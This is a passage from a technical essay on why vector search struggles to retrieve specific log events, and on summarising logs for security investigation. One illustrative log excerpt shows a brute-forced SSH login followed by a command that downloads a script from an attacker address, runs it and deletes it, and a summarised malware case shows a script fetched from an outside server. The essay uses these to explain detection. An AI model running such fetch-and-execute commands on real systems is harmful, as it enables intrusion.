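An embedding model learns from the contexts in which words occur. "Restart" and "reload" occur in similar sentences, so their vectors can end up close together. But no public text describes this fleet's host web-03. The model may split the name into fragments such as "web", "-" and "03", which indicate only that the host has something to do with the web and that its name resembles web-08.

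Pavani, Aluri and colleagues (2026), in *Entity Resolution in Practice*, describe this problem in a system that finds records of the same person, restaurant or song. They report that exact identifiers and codes provide "no useful gradient in the embedding space", so a vector search may fail to match two records that have the same code but different wording. On a dataset of five million records, their vector search found 97.8 per cent of the true pairs. An exact-match index over the identifier fields found seven more, raising the figure to 98.1 per cent. The gain was small, presumably because most matching records also had similar text in their other fields. The other text in log lines offers no such help, because A and B are identical apart from their identifiers and times.

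Short names cause similar problems. *Pre-Trained Language Models as Zero-Shot Tools for Social Science Research* (2026) reports that an embedding model places "OKC" near "Oklahoma City" but doesn't necessarily place the misspelling "Montegomery" near "Montgomery". A search that compares short runs of letters handles misspellings well but abbreviations poorly. On place names without a country or region, removing the letter-based search lowered accuracy by about one percentage point, so embeddings alone were enough for most names. For hostnames, however, tolerating small differences is a fault, because a comparison by letters would match web-03 with web-08 almost as well as with itself.

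Teng, Li and Chen (2025), in *LLMLog*, make what looks like the opposite complaint, that embeddings pay identifiers too much attention. Their system picks solved examples to show a language model that has to work out the template of a new log line. Suppose the new line is `com.cse.ust.hk:8080 POST`, where POST is the web command for sending data, and two solved examples are available:

```
proxy.cse.cuhk.edu.hk:5070 POST
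com.cse.ust.hk:8080 GET
```

Of the two examples, the first is more useful because it shows how to treat POST, but cosine similarity selects the second, which repeats the long address. Teng and colleagues conclude that the measure gives more weight to long words, such as timestamps and addresses, than to short keywords.

Their formula averages one vector per word, and this averaging alone would give the address and POST equal weight. If a model instead splits words into fragments and averages those, words with more fragments get more weight. For example, if the address yields nine fragments and POST yields one, the address contributes nine tenths of the average. Current embedding models adjust each fragment's vector to its context before combining them, so the number of fragments is only a rough guide to a word's influence.

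This also reconciles the two complaints. In line A, the timestamp might split into a dozen fragments and the hostname into three, so the timestamp would affect the vector more, even though hardly any question includes an exact second. Each part's weight depends on its length and the model's training, regardless of how much that part matters to a given question. Teng and colleagues need the verb and can ignore the address, while an engineer auditing web-03 needs the hostname most.

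### One flag can reverse a command

Two firewall commands on web-31 might differ by a single letter:

```
iptables -A INPUT -s 203.0.113.7 -j DROP
iptables -D INPUT -s 203.0.113.7 -j DROP
```

The first command adds a rule that blocks all traffic from the address, and the second deletes that rule. An agent that confuses them will tell an investigator that the address was blocked when someone had just unblocked it.

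Kapoor and Khan (2026), in *ExecRetrieval*, measured how well embeddings separate such near-copies in Python code. They assembled 939 tasks, each with a description in plain English, a correct function and up to four faulty versions. Each faulty version contains one targeted edit, such as a changed comparison or two swapped arguments, and fails at least one test when run. The best of 23 embedding setups, Gemini Embedding 2, ranked a correct function first as follows:

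| Faulty versions of the function in the store | Correct function ranked first | Random choice among the versions |
|---|---|---|
| None | 99.3% | 100% |
| One | 67.8% | 50% |
| Four | 33.1% | 20% |

The model ranked the right function above its faulty copies only somewhat more often than guessing would. When it ranked a wrong function first, that function was a faulty copy of the right one in 99.4 per cent of cases. In tests with four of the models, the embeddings mistook functions with two to four faults for the right one about as often as functions with one fault. Any advantage of Qwen3's 8-billion-parameter model over its 4-billion-parameter model was small enough to be due to chance.

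The same weakness appears in prose. In *Coverage Under Contradiction*, Abrishamchian, Yang and colleagues (2026) used a language model to reverse one claim in each document, then compared the search scores of the original and edited versions. One edit changed a statement that a child's white blood cell count "will return to normal" to say that it often remains elevated. When the edit changed less than 2 per cent of the characters, the embedding models Qwen3 and Jina scored the original higher in 58 and 56 per cent of pairs, close to the 50 per cent expected by chance. BM25 scored the original higher in 84 per cent.

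However, BM25 doesn't account for negation. It can rank the original higher only because the edit removed a query word or made the text longer. Matching exact words is still useful for commands, because a word index that keeps `-A` and `-D` as separate entries can distinguish the two firewall rules. But many indexes discard punctuation and ignore case.

### Thousands of lines from one template

Programs write log lines by filling values into a fixed pattern, the template. For the restart in lines A and B it is:

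```
<time> <host> user=<user> pid=<number> cmd="sudo systemctl restart shop-app" exit=<code>
```

Suppose the deploy account restarts the application once a day on every server. After 90 days the log contains 3,600 lines with this template, and a question about the restart of web-03 on 21 October has one correct line among them. If the search returns ten lines, the chance that it includes the right one depends on what the embeddings preserve:

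```
only the template:               10 / 3,600 ≈ 0.3%
the template and the host:       10 / 90    ≈ 11%
the template, host and date:     certain
```

The agent is therefore likely to miss the line even with a perfect encoding of the hostname. Fetching 100 results instead of ten would raise the chance of finding it to only 2.8 per cent in the first case, but would make finding it certain in the second.

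Tables with the same columns pose the same problem. *Semantically Similar, Yet Not Answerable* (Tian, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested current models on 209 questions, each with its own group of tables, made up of one that contained the answer and several siblings altered to remove it. In the paper's illustration, a question about deliveries overdue by more than two weeks in the third quarter of 2023 retrieves a table about the wrong period because that table includes the value "14 days". The best embedding model ranked a table from the right group first for 67.0 per cent of questions, but the right table first for only 18.2 per cent. When it found the right group, it therefore chose the right table 27 per cent of the time. A random choice would succeed 22 or 30 per cent of the time, depending on whether siblings with deleted columns count.

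Tian and colleagues repeated the test with naturally occurring tables that hold different portions of the same data, because artificial siblings might be unusually hard to tell apart. The gap between finding the right group and finding the right table widened. Jina's model found the right group for 94.8 per cent of questions and the right table for 14.3 per cent. The models' output also changed little when values no longer matched their columns. In a network record, that would mean confusing a connection from the web server to the database with one from the database to the web server.

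Word matching and combined searches didn't substantially narrow the gap in these tests. Using a second model to rerank the candidates by whether they could answer the question raised the share of right tables ranked first from 18.2 to 57.4 per cent. Reranking could help with log lines too, but when 3,600 of them share a template, the right one often won't be among the candidates.

The shared template helps with some tasks. *Log Anomaly Detection with Large Language Models via Knowledge-Enriched Fusion* (2025) retrieves known log entries to help a language model decide whether a new one is abnormal. Four embedding models of different sizes and ages gave almost the same results, because the task only requires entries with the same template as the new one, and the retrieved entries usually have it. *LogSieve* (2026) used embeddings to sort lines from automated software builds into those that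 help explain a failure and those that don't. With vectors from BERT, a language model from 2018, a simple classifier was right 97 per cent of the time. Both tasks depend on the kind of line, which embeddings represent well, but answering the engineer's question about web-03 requires finding a specific line.

### Relations that no single line contains

The host record of the nginx reload could look like this:

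```
{"time": "2026-10-21T09:16:51Z", "host": "web-03", "event": "process_start",
 "pid": 31905, "parent_pid": 31902, "user": "root", "exe": "/usr/sbin/nginx"}
```

On its own, the record shows that root, the administrator account, started nginx, and the deploy account doesn't appear in it. To learn that deploy was responsible, the agent has to match the parent process number, 31902, to the process number in line C. Linux reuses process numbers, so the two entries must also come from the same host and about the same time.

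An embedding model processes each entry separately, so its vector for this record can reflect the number 31902 but not the fact that another entry contains the same number. The agent could find the connection by comparing vectors only if both vectors preserved the number exactly, and even then it would be simpler to compare the numbers directly.

Sometimes the text of a log line doesn't show whether the line is important. In Windows logs from 12 machines, Verma and Bridges found that every infection with the ransomware CryptoWall 3.0 began with a Flash Player installer starting. The same entry also appeared during ordinary operation, presumably for genuine updates. Since identical text produces identical vectors, an embedding of that entry alone cannot separate an attack from an update. Later events, such as a temporary file with a random name opening Windows Explorer, distinguish the attack.

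*Corporate-Family Resolution Is Not a String-Matching Problem* (2026) measured how much this matters for company names by testing whether programs could tell that two companies belong to the same corporate group. Embeddings from MiniLM, a small general model, identified 64.3 per cent of the pairs whose names made the connection visible, but only 4.7 per cent of the pairs whose names didn't. Comparing three-letter sequences identified 4.2 per cent of the second kind.

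A larger model might do better with companies, because news articles and encyclopedias describe which company owns which. But only the other log entries record which process on web-03 started which.

### Numbers and times

An investigator may need every process that used more than 700 MB of memory, or every login between 02:00 and 03:00. *Revealing the Numeracy Gap* (Deng, Duan and colleagues, 2025) tests whether embeddings support numerical comparisons like these. It uses 1,000 financial questions, each with two answers that differ only in a number. For "Who owns over 15% of the company?", the correct answer says Alice owns 20% and the wrong one says she owns 5%. A model passes if it places the question closer to the correct answer than to the wrong one.

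The 13 models averaged 54 per cent accuracy across 18 ways of writing the numbers, where guessing would give 50. NV-Embed-v2 reached 74.2 per cent on numbers such as 0.8, but the models averaged 50.0 per cent on four-digit integers. Accuracy generally fell as the number of significant digits rose, which suggests that process numbers and timestamps would be difficult for these models. However, Deng and colleagues did not test timestamps, because they left out comparisons of dates and times as more complex.

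Surrounding text makes numbers even harder to distinguish. In one experiment, researchers inserted every number from 1 to 1,000 into the same sentence about a shareholder and measured the similarity of neighbouring versions. The similarities were close to 1, and much closer than those for the bare numbers. Reducing the questions to a form such as "Which number is above 200?" generally improved accuracy. A memory limit in a long log line is similarly hard to distinguish because the rest of the line determines most of the vector.

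More financial training didn't clearly help either, since a model adapted to finance did no better than the general model it was built on. Word matching can't replace embeddings here, because "over 15%" shares no more words with "20%" than with "5%". A program has to parse the values as numbers and compare them.

### Questions in prose, records in private code

Engineers ask questions in sentences, while records consist of commands, paths and codes. The question "Did anyone change how web-03 serves the site?" shares only the hostname with line C. Embeddings should handle this mismatch better than word matching, and in Kapoor and Khan's test they did. Even the weakest embedding model placed a correct function among the first ten results for 67.1 per cent of the descriptions, compared with 42.2 per cent for BM25.

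Slightly rewording the query can reverse that advantage. Xue and colleagues searched pandas, a Python library for data analysis, for the file affected by one change. When they searched for `DataFrame.reset_index` with the words "does not accept a tuple", BM25 ranked the right file first and vector search ranked it seventh. The change's original title mentioned the same function but also included the words "DOC" and "docs". With that title as the query, BM25 favoured documentation files and ranked the right file eighth, while vector search ranked it first. Across their queries, vector search did better mainly when the query lacked the code's rare words. Adding generated prose without identifiers made no difference.

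For system logs, Coskuner, Zeybel and Dolan (2026), in *LogRouter*, provide a direct comparison. They wrote 70 questions about public Linux, Apache, Windows and Mac logs, split the logs into passages of 25 lines, and measured recall among the first ten passages:

| Search | Recall@10 |
|---|---|
| Vector search | 15.4% |
| Both combined | 26.9% |
| Keyword search | 36.1% |

The measure favours keyword search because a passage counted as a hit only if it contained the text of the reference answer. The embedding model was also small enough for the team to run on its own hardware, and a 25-line passage can mix several unrelated events into one vector. Vector search performed poorly on logs in this test, but the result doesn't establish how the best current models would perform. Keyword search also missed almost two thirds of the relevant passages, so replacing vector search with it wouldn't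 be enough.

Coskuner and colleagues used their own hardware because public-sector logs are not allowed to leave the organisation. Such secrecy also limits the data anyone can learn from. Verma and Bridges, for example, obtained their Windows logs privately from a security team. Manuals and forums give public models many examples of how commands work, but few of a real fleet's log over three months.

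Shell commands also have a syntax that ordinary text tools don't parse correctly. In `java -Xms256m`, for example, no space separates the parameter's name from its value, while a `sed` command can contain a space that doesn't separate anything (Trizna, 2021, *Shell Language Processing*). Trizna trained a classifier to recognise malicious commands, using different methods to split them into tokens. The classifier found 78.9 per cent of the malicious commands with a splitter written for shell syntax and 24.4 per cent with a standard one. It was tested on the same commands it had learned from, so the figures show how well it could fit those commands with each splitter, not how well it would detect new attacks.

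Trizna also replaced every IP address and domain name with a placeholder and advised doing so in practice, because a model otherwise memorises the particular addresses in its training data. This suits a classifier, which has to recognise an attack from any address. In retrieval, masking the hostnames makes A and B even harder to tell apart, but a model trained on the fleet's unmasked logs may learn patterns specific to web-03 that don't apply to a server added next week.

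### Linking events in Amazon's cloud logs

In *An Evaluation Benchmark for Generative AI In Security Domain*, Ghashami, Kuznetsov and colleagues (2024) at Amazon tested how much training on logs can help. They compared RoBERTa-large, a general language model, with a copy they had trained further on logs from CloudTrail, the service that records what customers do in Amazon's cloud. These logs include the account, the user, the service they called and the operation they requested, which Amazon calls an API.

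One group of tests checks whether the model places events by the same user close together. Each of the 1,000 test cases contains an event that a user triggered, another event by that user, and ten events that the user never triggered. The model should place the second event closer to the first than the other ten. Every event has the same account and username, so the model has to rely on the rest of the event.

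The researchers report the scores as AUROC, the area under the receiver operating characteristic curve. It equals the probability that a randomly chosen true pair scores higher than a randomly chosen false pair, with ties counting as half. Suppose two true pairs have similarities of 0.9 and 0.6, and three false pairs have 0.8, 0.5 and 0.3:

```
0.9 is higher than 0.8, 0.5 and 0.3    3 of 3
0.6 is higher than 0.5 and 0.3         2 of 3
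AUROC = 5/6 ≈ 0.83
```

A perfect model scores 1, and a model that guesses scores 0.5. These were the results:

| What the model had to link | General model | Trained further on the logs |
|---|---|---|
| Services used by the same user | 0.52 | 0.63 |
| Services and APIs used by the same user | 0.50 | 0.66 |
| Whole events by the same user | 0.77 | 0.88 |
| IP addresses used by the same user | 0.58 | 0.60 |
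| The same predefined role in different accounts | 0.63 | 1.00 |

The general model linked services and APIs no better than chance, and the additional training raised its score to 0.66. Both models did better on whole events, perhaps because full records contain more values shared by one user's events.

The last two rows of the table show that training completely solved the test on roles but barely helped in the test on IP addresses. In the roles test, both texts include the name of the role, so the model only has to learn that the name matters more than the account number. In the IP address test, two unrelated addresses contain nothing to show that the same person used them.

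A score of 0.66 is also less useful for search than it may seem. If it held for individual comparisons, a related event in a store with 1,000 unrelated ones would rank behind about 340 of them on average. With a score of 0.88, it would still rank behind about 120. These are rough estimates, because Ghashami and colleagues averaged the similarities of the ten false pairs in each case and compared that average with the similarity of the true pair.

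The baseline was also weak, because RoBERTa-large was trained only to fill in missing words and lacked the training that embedding models need to place similar sentences close together. In Deng and colleagues' test of numbers, a RoBERTa model scored between 47 and 53 per cent in every format, while Qwen3-Embedding-8B reached 62.5 per cent on single-digit numbers. A current embedding model might therefore do better than 0.50 on CloudTrail. The trained model had an advantage that it would lack with new users, because the events in the true pairs came from its training data.

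Ghashami and colleagues recommend regularly rebuilding both the model and the test because accounts and users appear in the logs every day while others disappear. When they rebuilt the test daily for a week, the trained model stayed ahead each time. They left plain-language search of the logs to future work, so the benchmark measures whether related events lie close together, but not whether an engineer's question would find them.

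### What a better model can fix

These causes differ in whether better embeddings could remove them:

| Cause | Effect of a better embedding model |
|---|---|
| Questions and records use different words | Can remove much of it, especially after training on commands |
| Unfamiliar syntax | Can remove it with enough examples |
| One flag reverses a command | Can reduce it, but near-copies will still have similar scores |
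| Numbers and times | Can reduce it, but exact comparisons still need the values |
| Private names and new hosts | Can preserve the name, but not supply facts about the machine |
| Thousands of lines share a template | Helps only if the vector preserves every value that sets them apart |
| The relation depends on other entries | Can't remove it while the model embeds each entry alone |

Training a model to notice small differences can make it worse at other searches. *Training for Compositional Sensitivity Reduces Dense Retrieval Generalization* (2026) added almost 24,000 near-misses, such as sentences with a flipped negation or a changed word order, to 100,000 ordinary search examples, and the trained models generalised less well. Tian and colleagues taught a model to prefer tables that contain the answer, but the skill transferred poorly to other kinds of table. Combining this training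 with ordinary search training didn't preserve the full benefit of either.

That trade-off makes little sense for hosts, times and process numbers. To pick one restart out of 3,600, a vector would have to preserve the hostname and date exactly, and the log already contains both in fixed places. Better embeddings are more useful for the command itself, which can be worded in many ways.

Text embeddings group log entries by the kind of event but do poorly at identifying a particular event or its connections to others. Engineers sometimes say that logs have "no text embeddings", but an embedding model returns a vector for any text it can read, including line A. Tests of CmdCaliper, an embedding model for command lines, found that general models also capture part of a command's meaning. In Amazon's study, a program that looked for abnormal activity raised 4,594 alerts on mostly harmless logs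 when it started with random vectors. When it started with vectors from the general model, it raised 3,117 alerts but detected 4.5 per cent fewer simulated attacks.

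## Summarising records before embedding them

Embedding models handle sentences better than log lines, so a program can turn the lines into sentences first. It groups related records, counts the events in them and writes a short description for the vector index. A search finds the description, which links back to the original lines. The method suits questions about patterns, such as a run of failed logins, because no single line contains the pattern.

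### Ten lines and two summaries

These ten lines appear in the logs of web-22 and web-09 early on 3 November. The program `sshd` handles remote logins, `wget` downloads a file, `bash` runs it as a script and `rm` deletes it.

```
 1  2026-11-03T03:12:04Z web-22 sshd[5101]: Failed password for deploy from 198.51.100.24 port 51122
 2  2026-11-03T03:12:09Z web-22 sshd[5104]: Failed password for deploy from 198.51.100.24 port 51130
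 3  2026-11-03T03:12:15Z web-22 sshd[5107]: Failed password for deploy from 198.51.100.24 port 51138
 4  2026-11-03T03:12:22Z web-22 sshd[5110]: Failed password for deploy from 198.51.100.24 port 51144
 5  2026-11-03T03:12:31Z web-22 sshd[5113]: Accepted password for deploy from 198.51.100.24 port 51152
 6  2026-11-03T03:13:20Z web-22 user=deploy pid=5144 cmd="wget http://198.51.100.24/u.sh" exit=0
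 7  2026-11-03T03:13:31Z web-22 user=deploy pid=5149 cmd="bash u.sh" exit=0
 8  2026-11-03T03:20:02Z web-09 user=deploy pid=8816 cmd="sudo systemctl restart shop-app" exit=0
 9  2026-11-03T03:20:40Z web-09 user=deploy pid=8840 cmd="systemctl status shop-app" exit=0
10  2026-11-03T03:41:17Z web-22 user=deploy pid=5302 cmd="rm u.sh" exit=0
```

The program first splits each line into its template and its values. If it treats the whole command as a value, three templates cover all ten lines:

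```
<time> <host> sshd[<pid>]: Failed password for <user> from <source_ip> port <port>     lines 1–4
<time> <host> sshd[<pid>]: Accepted password for <user> from <source_ip> port <port>   line 5
<time> <host> user=<user> pid=<pid> cmd="<command>" exit=<code>                        lines 6–10
```

Next it stores the values under names that stay the same across templates, so that `user` is the account in both a login and a command. Line 5 becomes:

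```
{"time": "2026-11-03T03:12:31Z", "host": "web-22", "event": "login_accepted",
 "pid": 5113, "user": "deploy", "source_ip": "198.51.100.24", "port": 51152}
```

The program then groups the records by host and hour and counts each kind of event. Lines 8 and 9 form a group for web-09. The other eight form this one:

```
web-22, 3 November 2026, 03:00–04:00
login_failed     4   deploy from 198.51.100.24                    03:12:04–03:12:22
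login_accepted   1   deploy from 198.51.100.24                    03:12:31
command          3   deploy: wget …/u.sh, bash u.sh, rm u.sh      03:13:20–03:41:17
```

From the counts it writes a description and computes an embedding of it:

> On web-22, between 03:00 and 04:00 on 3 November 2026, four password logins for deploy from 198.51.100.24 failed, then one from the same address succeeded. The deploy user downloaded the script u.sh from that address, ran it and deleted it.

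Finally, the program saves the description with its host, its hour and the positions of the eight lines. An engineer who asks "Has anyone guessed a password and run something on our servers?" has a good chance of finding this description, whereas line 5 alone looks like any other login. Before acting on the description, the agent uses the saved positions to read the original lines, which also contain the exact times and process numbers.

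Either fixed rules or a language model can write the description. Rules always describe the same record in the same words and add no information to it. A model writes more naturally, but it may add an explanation that the record doesn't support, such as that an attacker guessed the password when an engineer had mistyped it four times. Like a decision record, the description should contain only observations, not explanations.

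The length of the time window is a compromise. Five-minute windows would divide the fleet's 90 days of commands into just over a million groups averaging 1.7 commands each, which hardly shortens the log. Hourly windows give 86,400 groups of about 21 commands.

Summaries don't make it easier to tell machines apart. The 3,600 daily restarts of the shop application would produce 3,600 summaries that differ mainly in host and date, so the program still needs to filter by those two fields.

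### Finding the templates

Writing templates by hand is slow. In *Semantic-Aware Parsing for Security Logs*, Piet, Fang and colleagues (2025) describe a 160-line program they had written just to extract successful connections from one SSH log. It contained a 3,616-character regular expression (a pattern that specifies which strings match).

Parsers find templates automatically. Drain, a widely used one, compares lines word by word under fixed rules. Newer parsers use a language model to identify the constant words. Running the model on every line is affordable for a small fleet. *HELP* (Xu and Gau, 2024) calculates that a million lines cost $51.45 with GPT-4o mini, so the fleet's 1.8 million would cost about $93. But some systems produce hundreds of millions of lines an hour, and a model may also write different templates for the same event. Most of these newer parsers therefore run the model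 once per template and reuse the result. This avoids most of the model calls, because logs have far fewer templates than lines. Loghub-2.0, a public collection of 14 logs, has over 50 million lines but fewer than 3,500 templates.

Xu and Gau group lines by embedding, then have a model write one template per group. They warn that ordinary embeddings can form groups that are too narrow, such as one per user or file path. They add each line's word count and train a small network to adjust the vectors. Groups could also be too broad, for example if two firewall commands that differ only in `-A` and `-D` ended up together.

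*Small Is Beautiful* (Wang and Huo, 2026) compared parsers on Loghub-2.0. All the parsers in this table except Drain used a small language model, Gemini 1.5 Flash-8B. EFParser is Wang and Huo's own parser. The last column is the F1 score, which combines precision (the share of a parser's templates that are correct) and recall (the share of the true templates that it finds).

| Parser | Lines grouped correctly | Lines split exactly right | Templates exactly right (F1) |
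|---|---|---|---|
| Drain | 84% | 47% | 28% |
| LILAC, without labelled examples | 83% | 61% | 52% |
| LUNAR | 89% | 76% | 72% |
| LogBatcher | 90% | 84% | 75% |
| EFParser | 92% | 89% | 78% |

A parser only needs to group log lines correctly to count events, but to get the fields right it must also split each line correctly. According to *LLM4Log* (2026), a review of log analysis with language models, benchmarks have made it clearer whether a new parser improves grouping or splitting.

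Per-line scores also hide errors in rare templates, because a few templates produce most of the lines. Drain's grouping score falls from 84 to 55 per cent when each template counts equally. Investigators often need the lines from rare templates. Current models would probably do better than the ones in this comparison, which are more than two years old.

A template that is too general damages a summary most. Wang and Huo give the example of a parser that turns "Database connection failed" into `Database connection <*>`. If a parser did the same to lines 1 to 5, the template would begin `<*> password for`, and the summary would count five password events but omit that the last one succeeded. EFParser reduces this risk by turning verbs back into constants. A template can also be too specific. For example, `Process apache2 terminated with exit code <*>` includes the program's name, so the same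 kind of event is counted separately for each program.

Engineers can avoid some of this guesswork for in-house software, such as the shop application, because they have the source code. *LLM-SrcLog* (2025) extracts log templates from the code in advance and matches incoming log lines to them with regular expressions.

### Giving the values consistent names

A template marks where the values are but not what they mean. In Matryoshka, a system built by Piet and colleagues, a language model writes the templates, with a regular expression for each value. It then gives each value a name and a description, using similar fields it has already named as examples. Without these examples, a model may call the same value `source_ip` in one template and `src_ip` in another, and a query for one name misses the other. Matryoshka can also map its fields to the Open Cybersecurity Schema Framework (OCSF),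 a public standard for naming security data.

The team tested this on logs that users had attached to public bug reports, with up to ten queries for each of five kinds of log. The table includes separate results for Linux audit logs, which are the closest of the five to the fleet's host records:

| Search | Precision, all logs | Recall, all logs | Precision, audit logs | Recall, audit logs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
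| Matryoshka's own fields | 96% | 95% | 90% | 88% |
| One matching string per query | 94% | 80% | 97% | 85% |
| OCSF fields | 66% | 69% | 70% | 68% |

Searching by Matryoshka's own fields found more than a string search did, but the advantage almost disappeared for audit logs. The parser sometimes stored the same kind of value under two names, such as `current_working_directory` and `cwd`. OCSF did worst because it has tens of thousands of attributes, many with overlapping definitions.

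The comparison favours Matryoshka because Piet and colleagues created the reference answers by correcting its output and tested the parsers on the same lines used to build them. The string search was also simple, as they acknowledge, and an experienced analyst would try several strings.

Building the parsers took from 26 minutes for the logs of scheduled jobs to 19 hours for the audit logs. They then processed over 200 lines a second, so a day of the fleet's commands would take less than two minutes. A line in a new format may match no template, so each summary should also include a count of the unmatched lines and a link to them.

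No language model reads the live log lines, so an attacker cannot manipulate the parser with instructions hidden in them. An agent that later reads the summaries can still be manipulated, because attackers can choose the usernames and file names that appear there.

### Whether descriptions make better embeddings

Matryoshka also has a model describe each log line in prose, then compares embeddings of the descriptions to decide which lines belong together. Piet and colleagues tested this on logs of network address assignments. Queries on the finished database had a precision of 100 per cent and a recall of 97 per cent with descriptions, compared with 90 and 81 per cent with ordinary embeddings. This is good evidence that descriptions helped to build a parser for one kind of log, but it doesn't directly measure whether an engineer's question would find the right line.

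Fixed rules can also write the descriptions. *NLLog* (Ndichu, Ban and colleagues, 2026) rewrites each template as a sentence with an actor, an action and a severity. For example, a cryptic supercomputer message about an "rts panic" becomes "Kernel runtime system encountered a panic and halted execution (fatal)". A classifier uses embeddings of these sentences to detect abnormal periods. On the supercomputer logs, the sentences raised its F1 score from 88.5 to 97.0 per cent.

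That gain is less impressive than it seems because the baseline used template identifiers such as "E23", which carry no useful meaning for an embedding model. When the rules just put the original template text between the component's name and the severity, the supercomputer score was about 97.5 per cent, the same as with full sentences. The wording mattered more on logs from Hadoop, a distributed file system. There the simple version scored 69.5 per cent and full sentences scored 99.8, but so did the bare identifiers. Ndichu and colleagues had to write special rules for 36 of the 44 Hadoop templates, though that work grows with the number of templates, not the number of lines.

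Rewriting can also remove useful differences between records. With a simple word-counting classifier, the rewritten sentences raised the supercomputer score from 82 to 92 per cent but lowered the Hadoop score from 94 to 85 per cent. The index should therefore keep the original text alongside the description.

The best embedding model may depend on what it embeds. *SecEncoder* (2024) presents a model trained on security logs and tests it on log search, using two definitions of relevance. When relevance meant having the same template, the model did slightly better than general models. When it meant having similar descriptions written by GPT-4, a general OpenAI model did slightly better on one measure and about equally well on the other. The descriptions may have suited OpenAI's embedding model, since OpenAI also made GPT-4. Still, a general embedding model is a reasonable first choice for prose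 summaries.

*Diagnosing and Resolving Cloud Platform Instability with Multi-modal RAG LLMs* (Wang and Birman, 2025) describes ARCA, a system for diagnosing faults in cloud software. ARCA filters logs instead of counting events, using a language model to keep only warnings, errors, special events and performance readings. It embeds what remains and searches for similar past incidents, then narrows the results by comparing figures such as processor and memory use. A model then picks the past incident that best matches the new one.

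The team caused faults in test applications and produced 800 bug tickets, 700 for the store and 100 for testing. Every fault was a processor overload, a memory leak, a network delay or a combination of overload and leak. The team ran each experiment twice, and ARCA had to match each test ticket to the one from the other run. The candidates included the matching ticket for up to 92 per cent of new tickets, and the model chose it for 74 per cent. The model chose correctly 72 per cent of the time with logs alone and 34 per cent with performance figures alone, so nearly all of its accuracy came from the logs.

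The 92 per cent is a weak result for the search itself, because ARCA retrieves hundreds of candidates. A random draw of 300 from 700 tickets would include the matching ticket 43 per cent of the time. Retrieving 400 candidates instead of 300 included the matching ticket more often but made the final choice worse. The tickets were probably easier than real ones, since a model wrote every description after being told the cause. Wang and Birman support the filtering step with a plot in which incidents with the same cause lie closer together after filtering, but they don't compare search accuracy with and without it.

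This kind of filter also depends on the fault leaving visible traces. In the ten lines above, it would probably keep the four failed logins, but the successful login is neither a warning nor an error.

### Three summaries joined by one address

*Retrieval-Augmented LLMs for Security Incident Analysis* (Cadet, Koh and colleagues, 2026) provides the most detailed test of counting before embedding. Its system answers questions about an attack, such as which machine it infected and which outside servers controlled that machine. The system searches a database of network alerts, connection records and Windows logins.

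The team wrote a library of database queries by hand. Each query selects one kind of event and counts it by user, address or another field. The program cuts the results into pieces, embeds them and stores the vectors. These pieces are lists of names and counts, not sentences. For each question, the program retrieves the closest pieces, normally seven, and gives them to a language model with a short description of the network. The model has to either answer from the evidence and list the pieces it used, or report that they don't contain the answer.

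In one case, a user had downloaded malware disguised as an authentication app, and the logs contained 3,694 events. Three summaries were enough to explain what had happened. In simplified form:

```
alerts      10.1.17.215: 6 high-severity alerts
logins      10.1.17.215: user shutchenson 11, machine DESKTOP-L8C5GSJ 10
downloads   10.1.17.215 -> 5.252.153.241: /api/file/get-file/29842.ps1, 4 times
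```

The alerts identify an infected address but no user. The login counts connect the address to a user and a machine, but those logins look normal. The download counts show a script and the server it came from, but not that the server was malicious. The vector search only had to retrieve these three summaries. Because all three contain the address 10.1.17.215, the language model could connect them and conclude that shutchenson's machine had downloaded a script from the attacker's server.

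The full test had 17 malware cases with 94,948 events and 129 questions. The cases and their answers came from public exercises for security analysts. The first four result columns give average recall for different values of k. The last column covers 42 questions whose answers were spread over at least two pieces.

| Model | k = 1 | k = 3 | k = 7 | k = 14 | Answer in several pieces |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
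| Claude Sonnet 4 | 39% | 72% | 94% | 94% | 89% |
| DeepSeek V3 | 35% | 71% | 89% | 89% | 78% |
| Llama 3.1 70B | 40% | 68% | 81% | 78% | 56% |
| Cisco Foundation-Sec-8B | 43% | 62% | 71% | 67% | 46% |
| GPT-4o | 46% | 59% | 69% | 64% | 53% |
| GPT-5.2 | 46% | 62% | 68% | 64% | 52% |
| GPT-4 | 46% | 60% | 67% | 66% | 52% |
| GPT-5-mini | 44% | 62% | 64% | 66% | 47% |

Claude often answered "Not found" when given one piece, while the OpenAI models extracted an answer from whatever they had. With seven pieces, Claude was far ahead because it combined them better. Cisco's security model did worse than the general Llama model, but Cisco's is also much smaller. DeepSeek's analysis cost less than a cent per case, and Claude's cost 12 cents.

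Measuring only recall overrates models that list every suspicious address. On questions with several correct items, 76 per cent of the items Claude listed matched the reference answers, compared with 29 per cent for GPT-5.2. In one case GPT-5.2 named five possible control servers, two of which belonged to Microsoft, while DeepSeek named only the correct one. Some unmatched items may still have been malicious, because the reference answers include only confirmed ones.

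In a separate exercise, professional testers attacked a Windows network run with Active Directory, Microsoft's system for managing accounts and machines. Claude and DeepSeek each found 25 of the 26 attack steps, and neither reported a false one. One summary recorded a request for a certificate in the administrator's name, and another recorded that the network had issued the certificate to an ordinary user. Both models' results depended on having such summaries together, because neither event is suspicious on its own.

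### What the vector search contributed

These results show that a language model can reconstruct an attack from a few well-chosen counts, but they provide much less evidence about vector search. In the Active Directory exercise, nine queries produced nine summaries, and the program retrieved all nine at once, so the 96 per cent recall did not depend on the search selecting the right ones.

In the malware cases, the search did have to choose, and k made a large difference. But the queries for those cases cover only six attack techniques, so there were few summaries to choose from. For one question about the fake authentication app, the seven retrieved pieces came from four kinds of summary. Recall may have stopped rising after k = 7 because seven pieces already contained most of the useful information. Measuring what the search adds would require comparing it with seven random pieces and with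 a prompt that contains every piece. A store with 86,400 hourly summaries would be a far harder test than any of these cases.

The 94 per cent also applies to attacks that someone had already prepared for. Cadet and colleagues developed the queries step by step for the kinds of attack in the test and checked them against known attack data, an advantage the queries wouldn't have against a new attack. The team changed the queries specifically for IcedID, a program that steals banking details. The standard version ignored traffic to googleapis.com as harmless, but the malware had arrived from a Google storage address, so they narrowed that exclusion and added two counts, which recovered two of the attacker's addresses. Together, the query libraries cover 16 of about 200 techniques in MITRE ATT&CK, a public catalogue of attack methods.

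Cadet and colleagues compared summaries with raw logs on the fake authentication case and concluded that preprocessing is essential. Claude and DeepSeek had a recall of 100 per cent with summaries and 50 per cent with raw events. But Claude received only the first 158 of the 3,694 raw events (4.3 per cent), and DeepSeek received 104. The malicious servers appeared only later in the log, so no model could have found them in the raw events it received. GPT-5.2 can read far more text than GPT-4 but received the same 22 events, which suggests that the program applied one limit to all OpenAI models.

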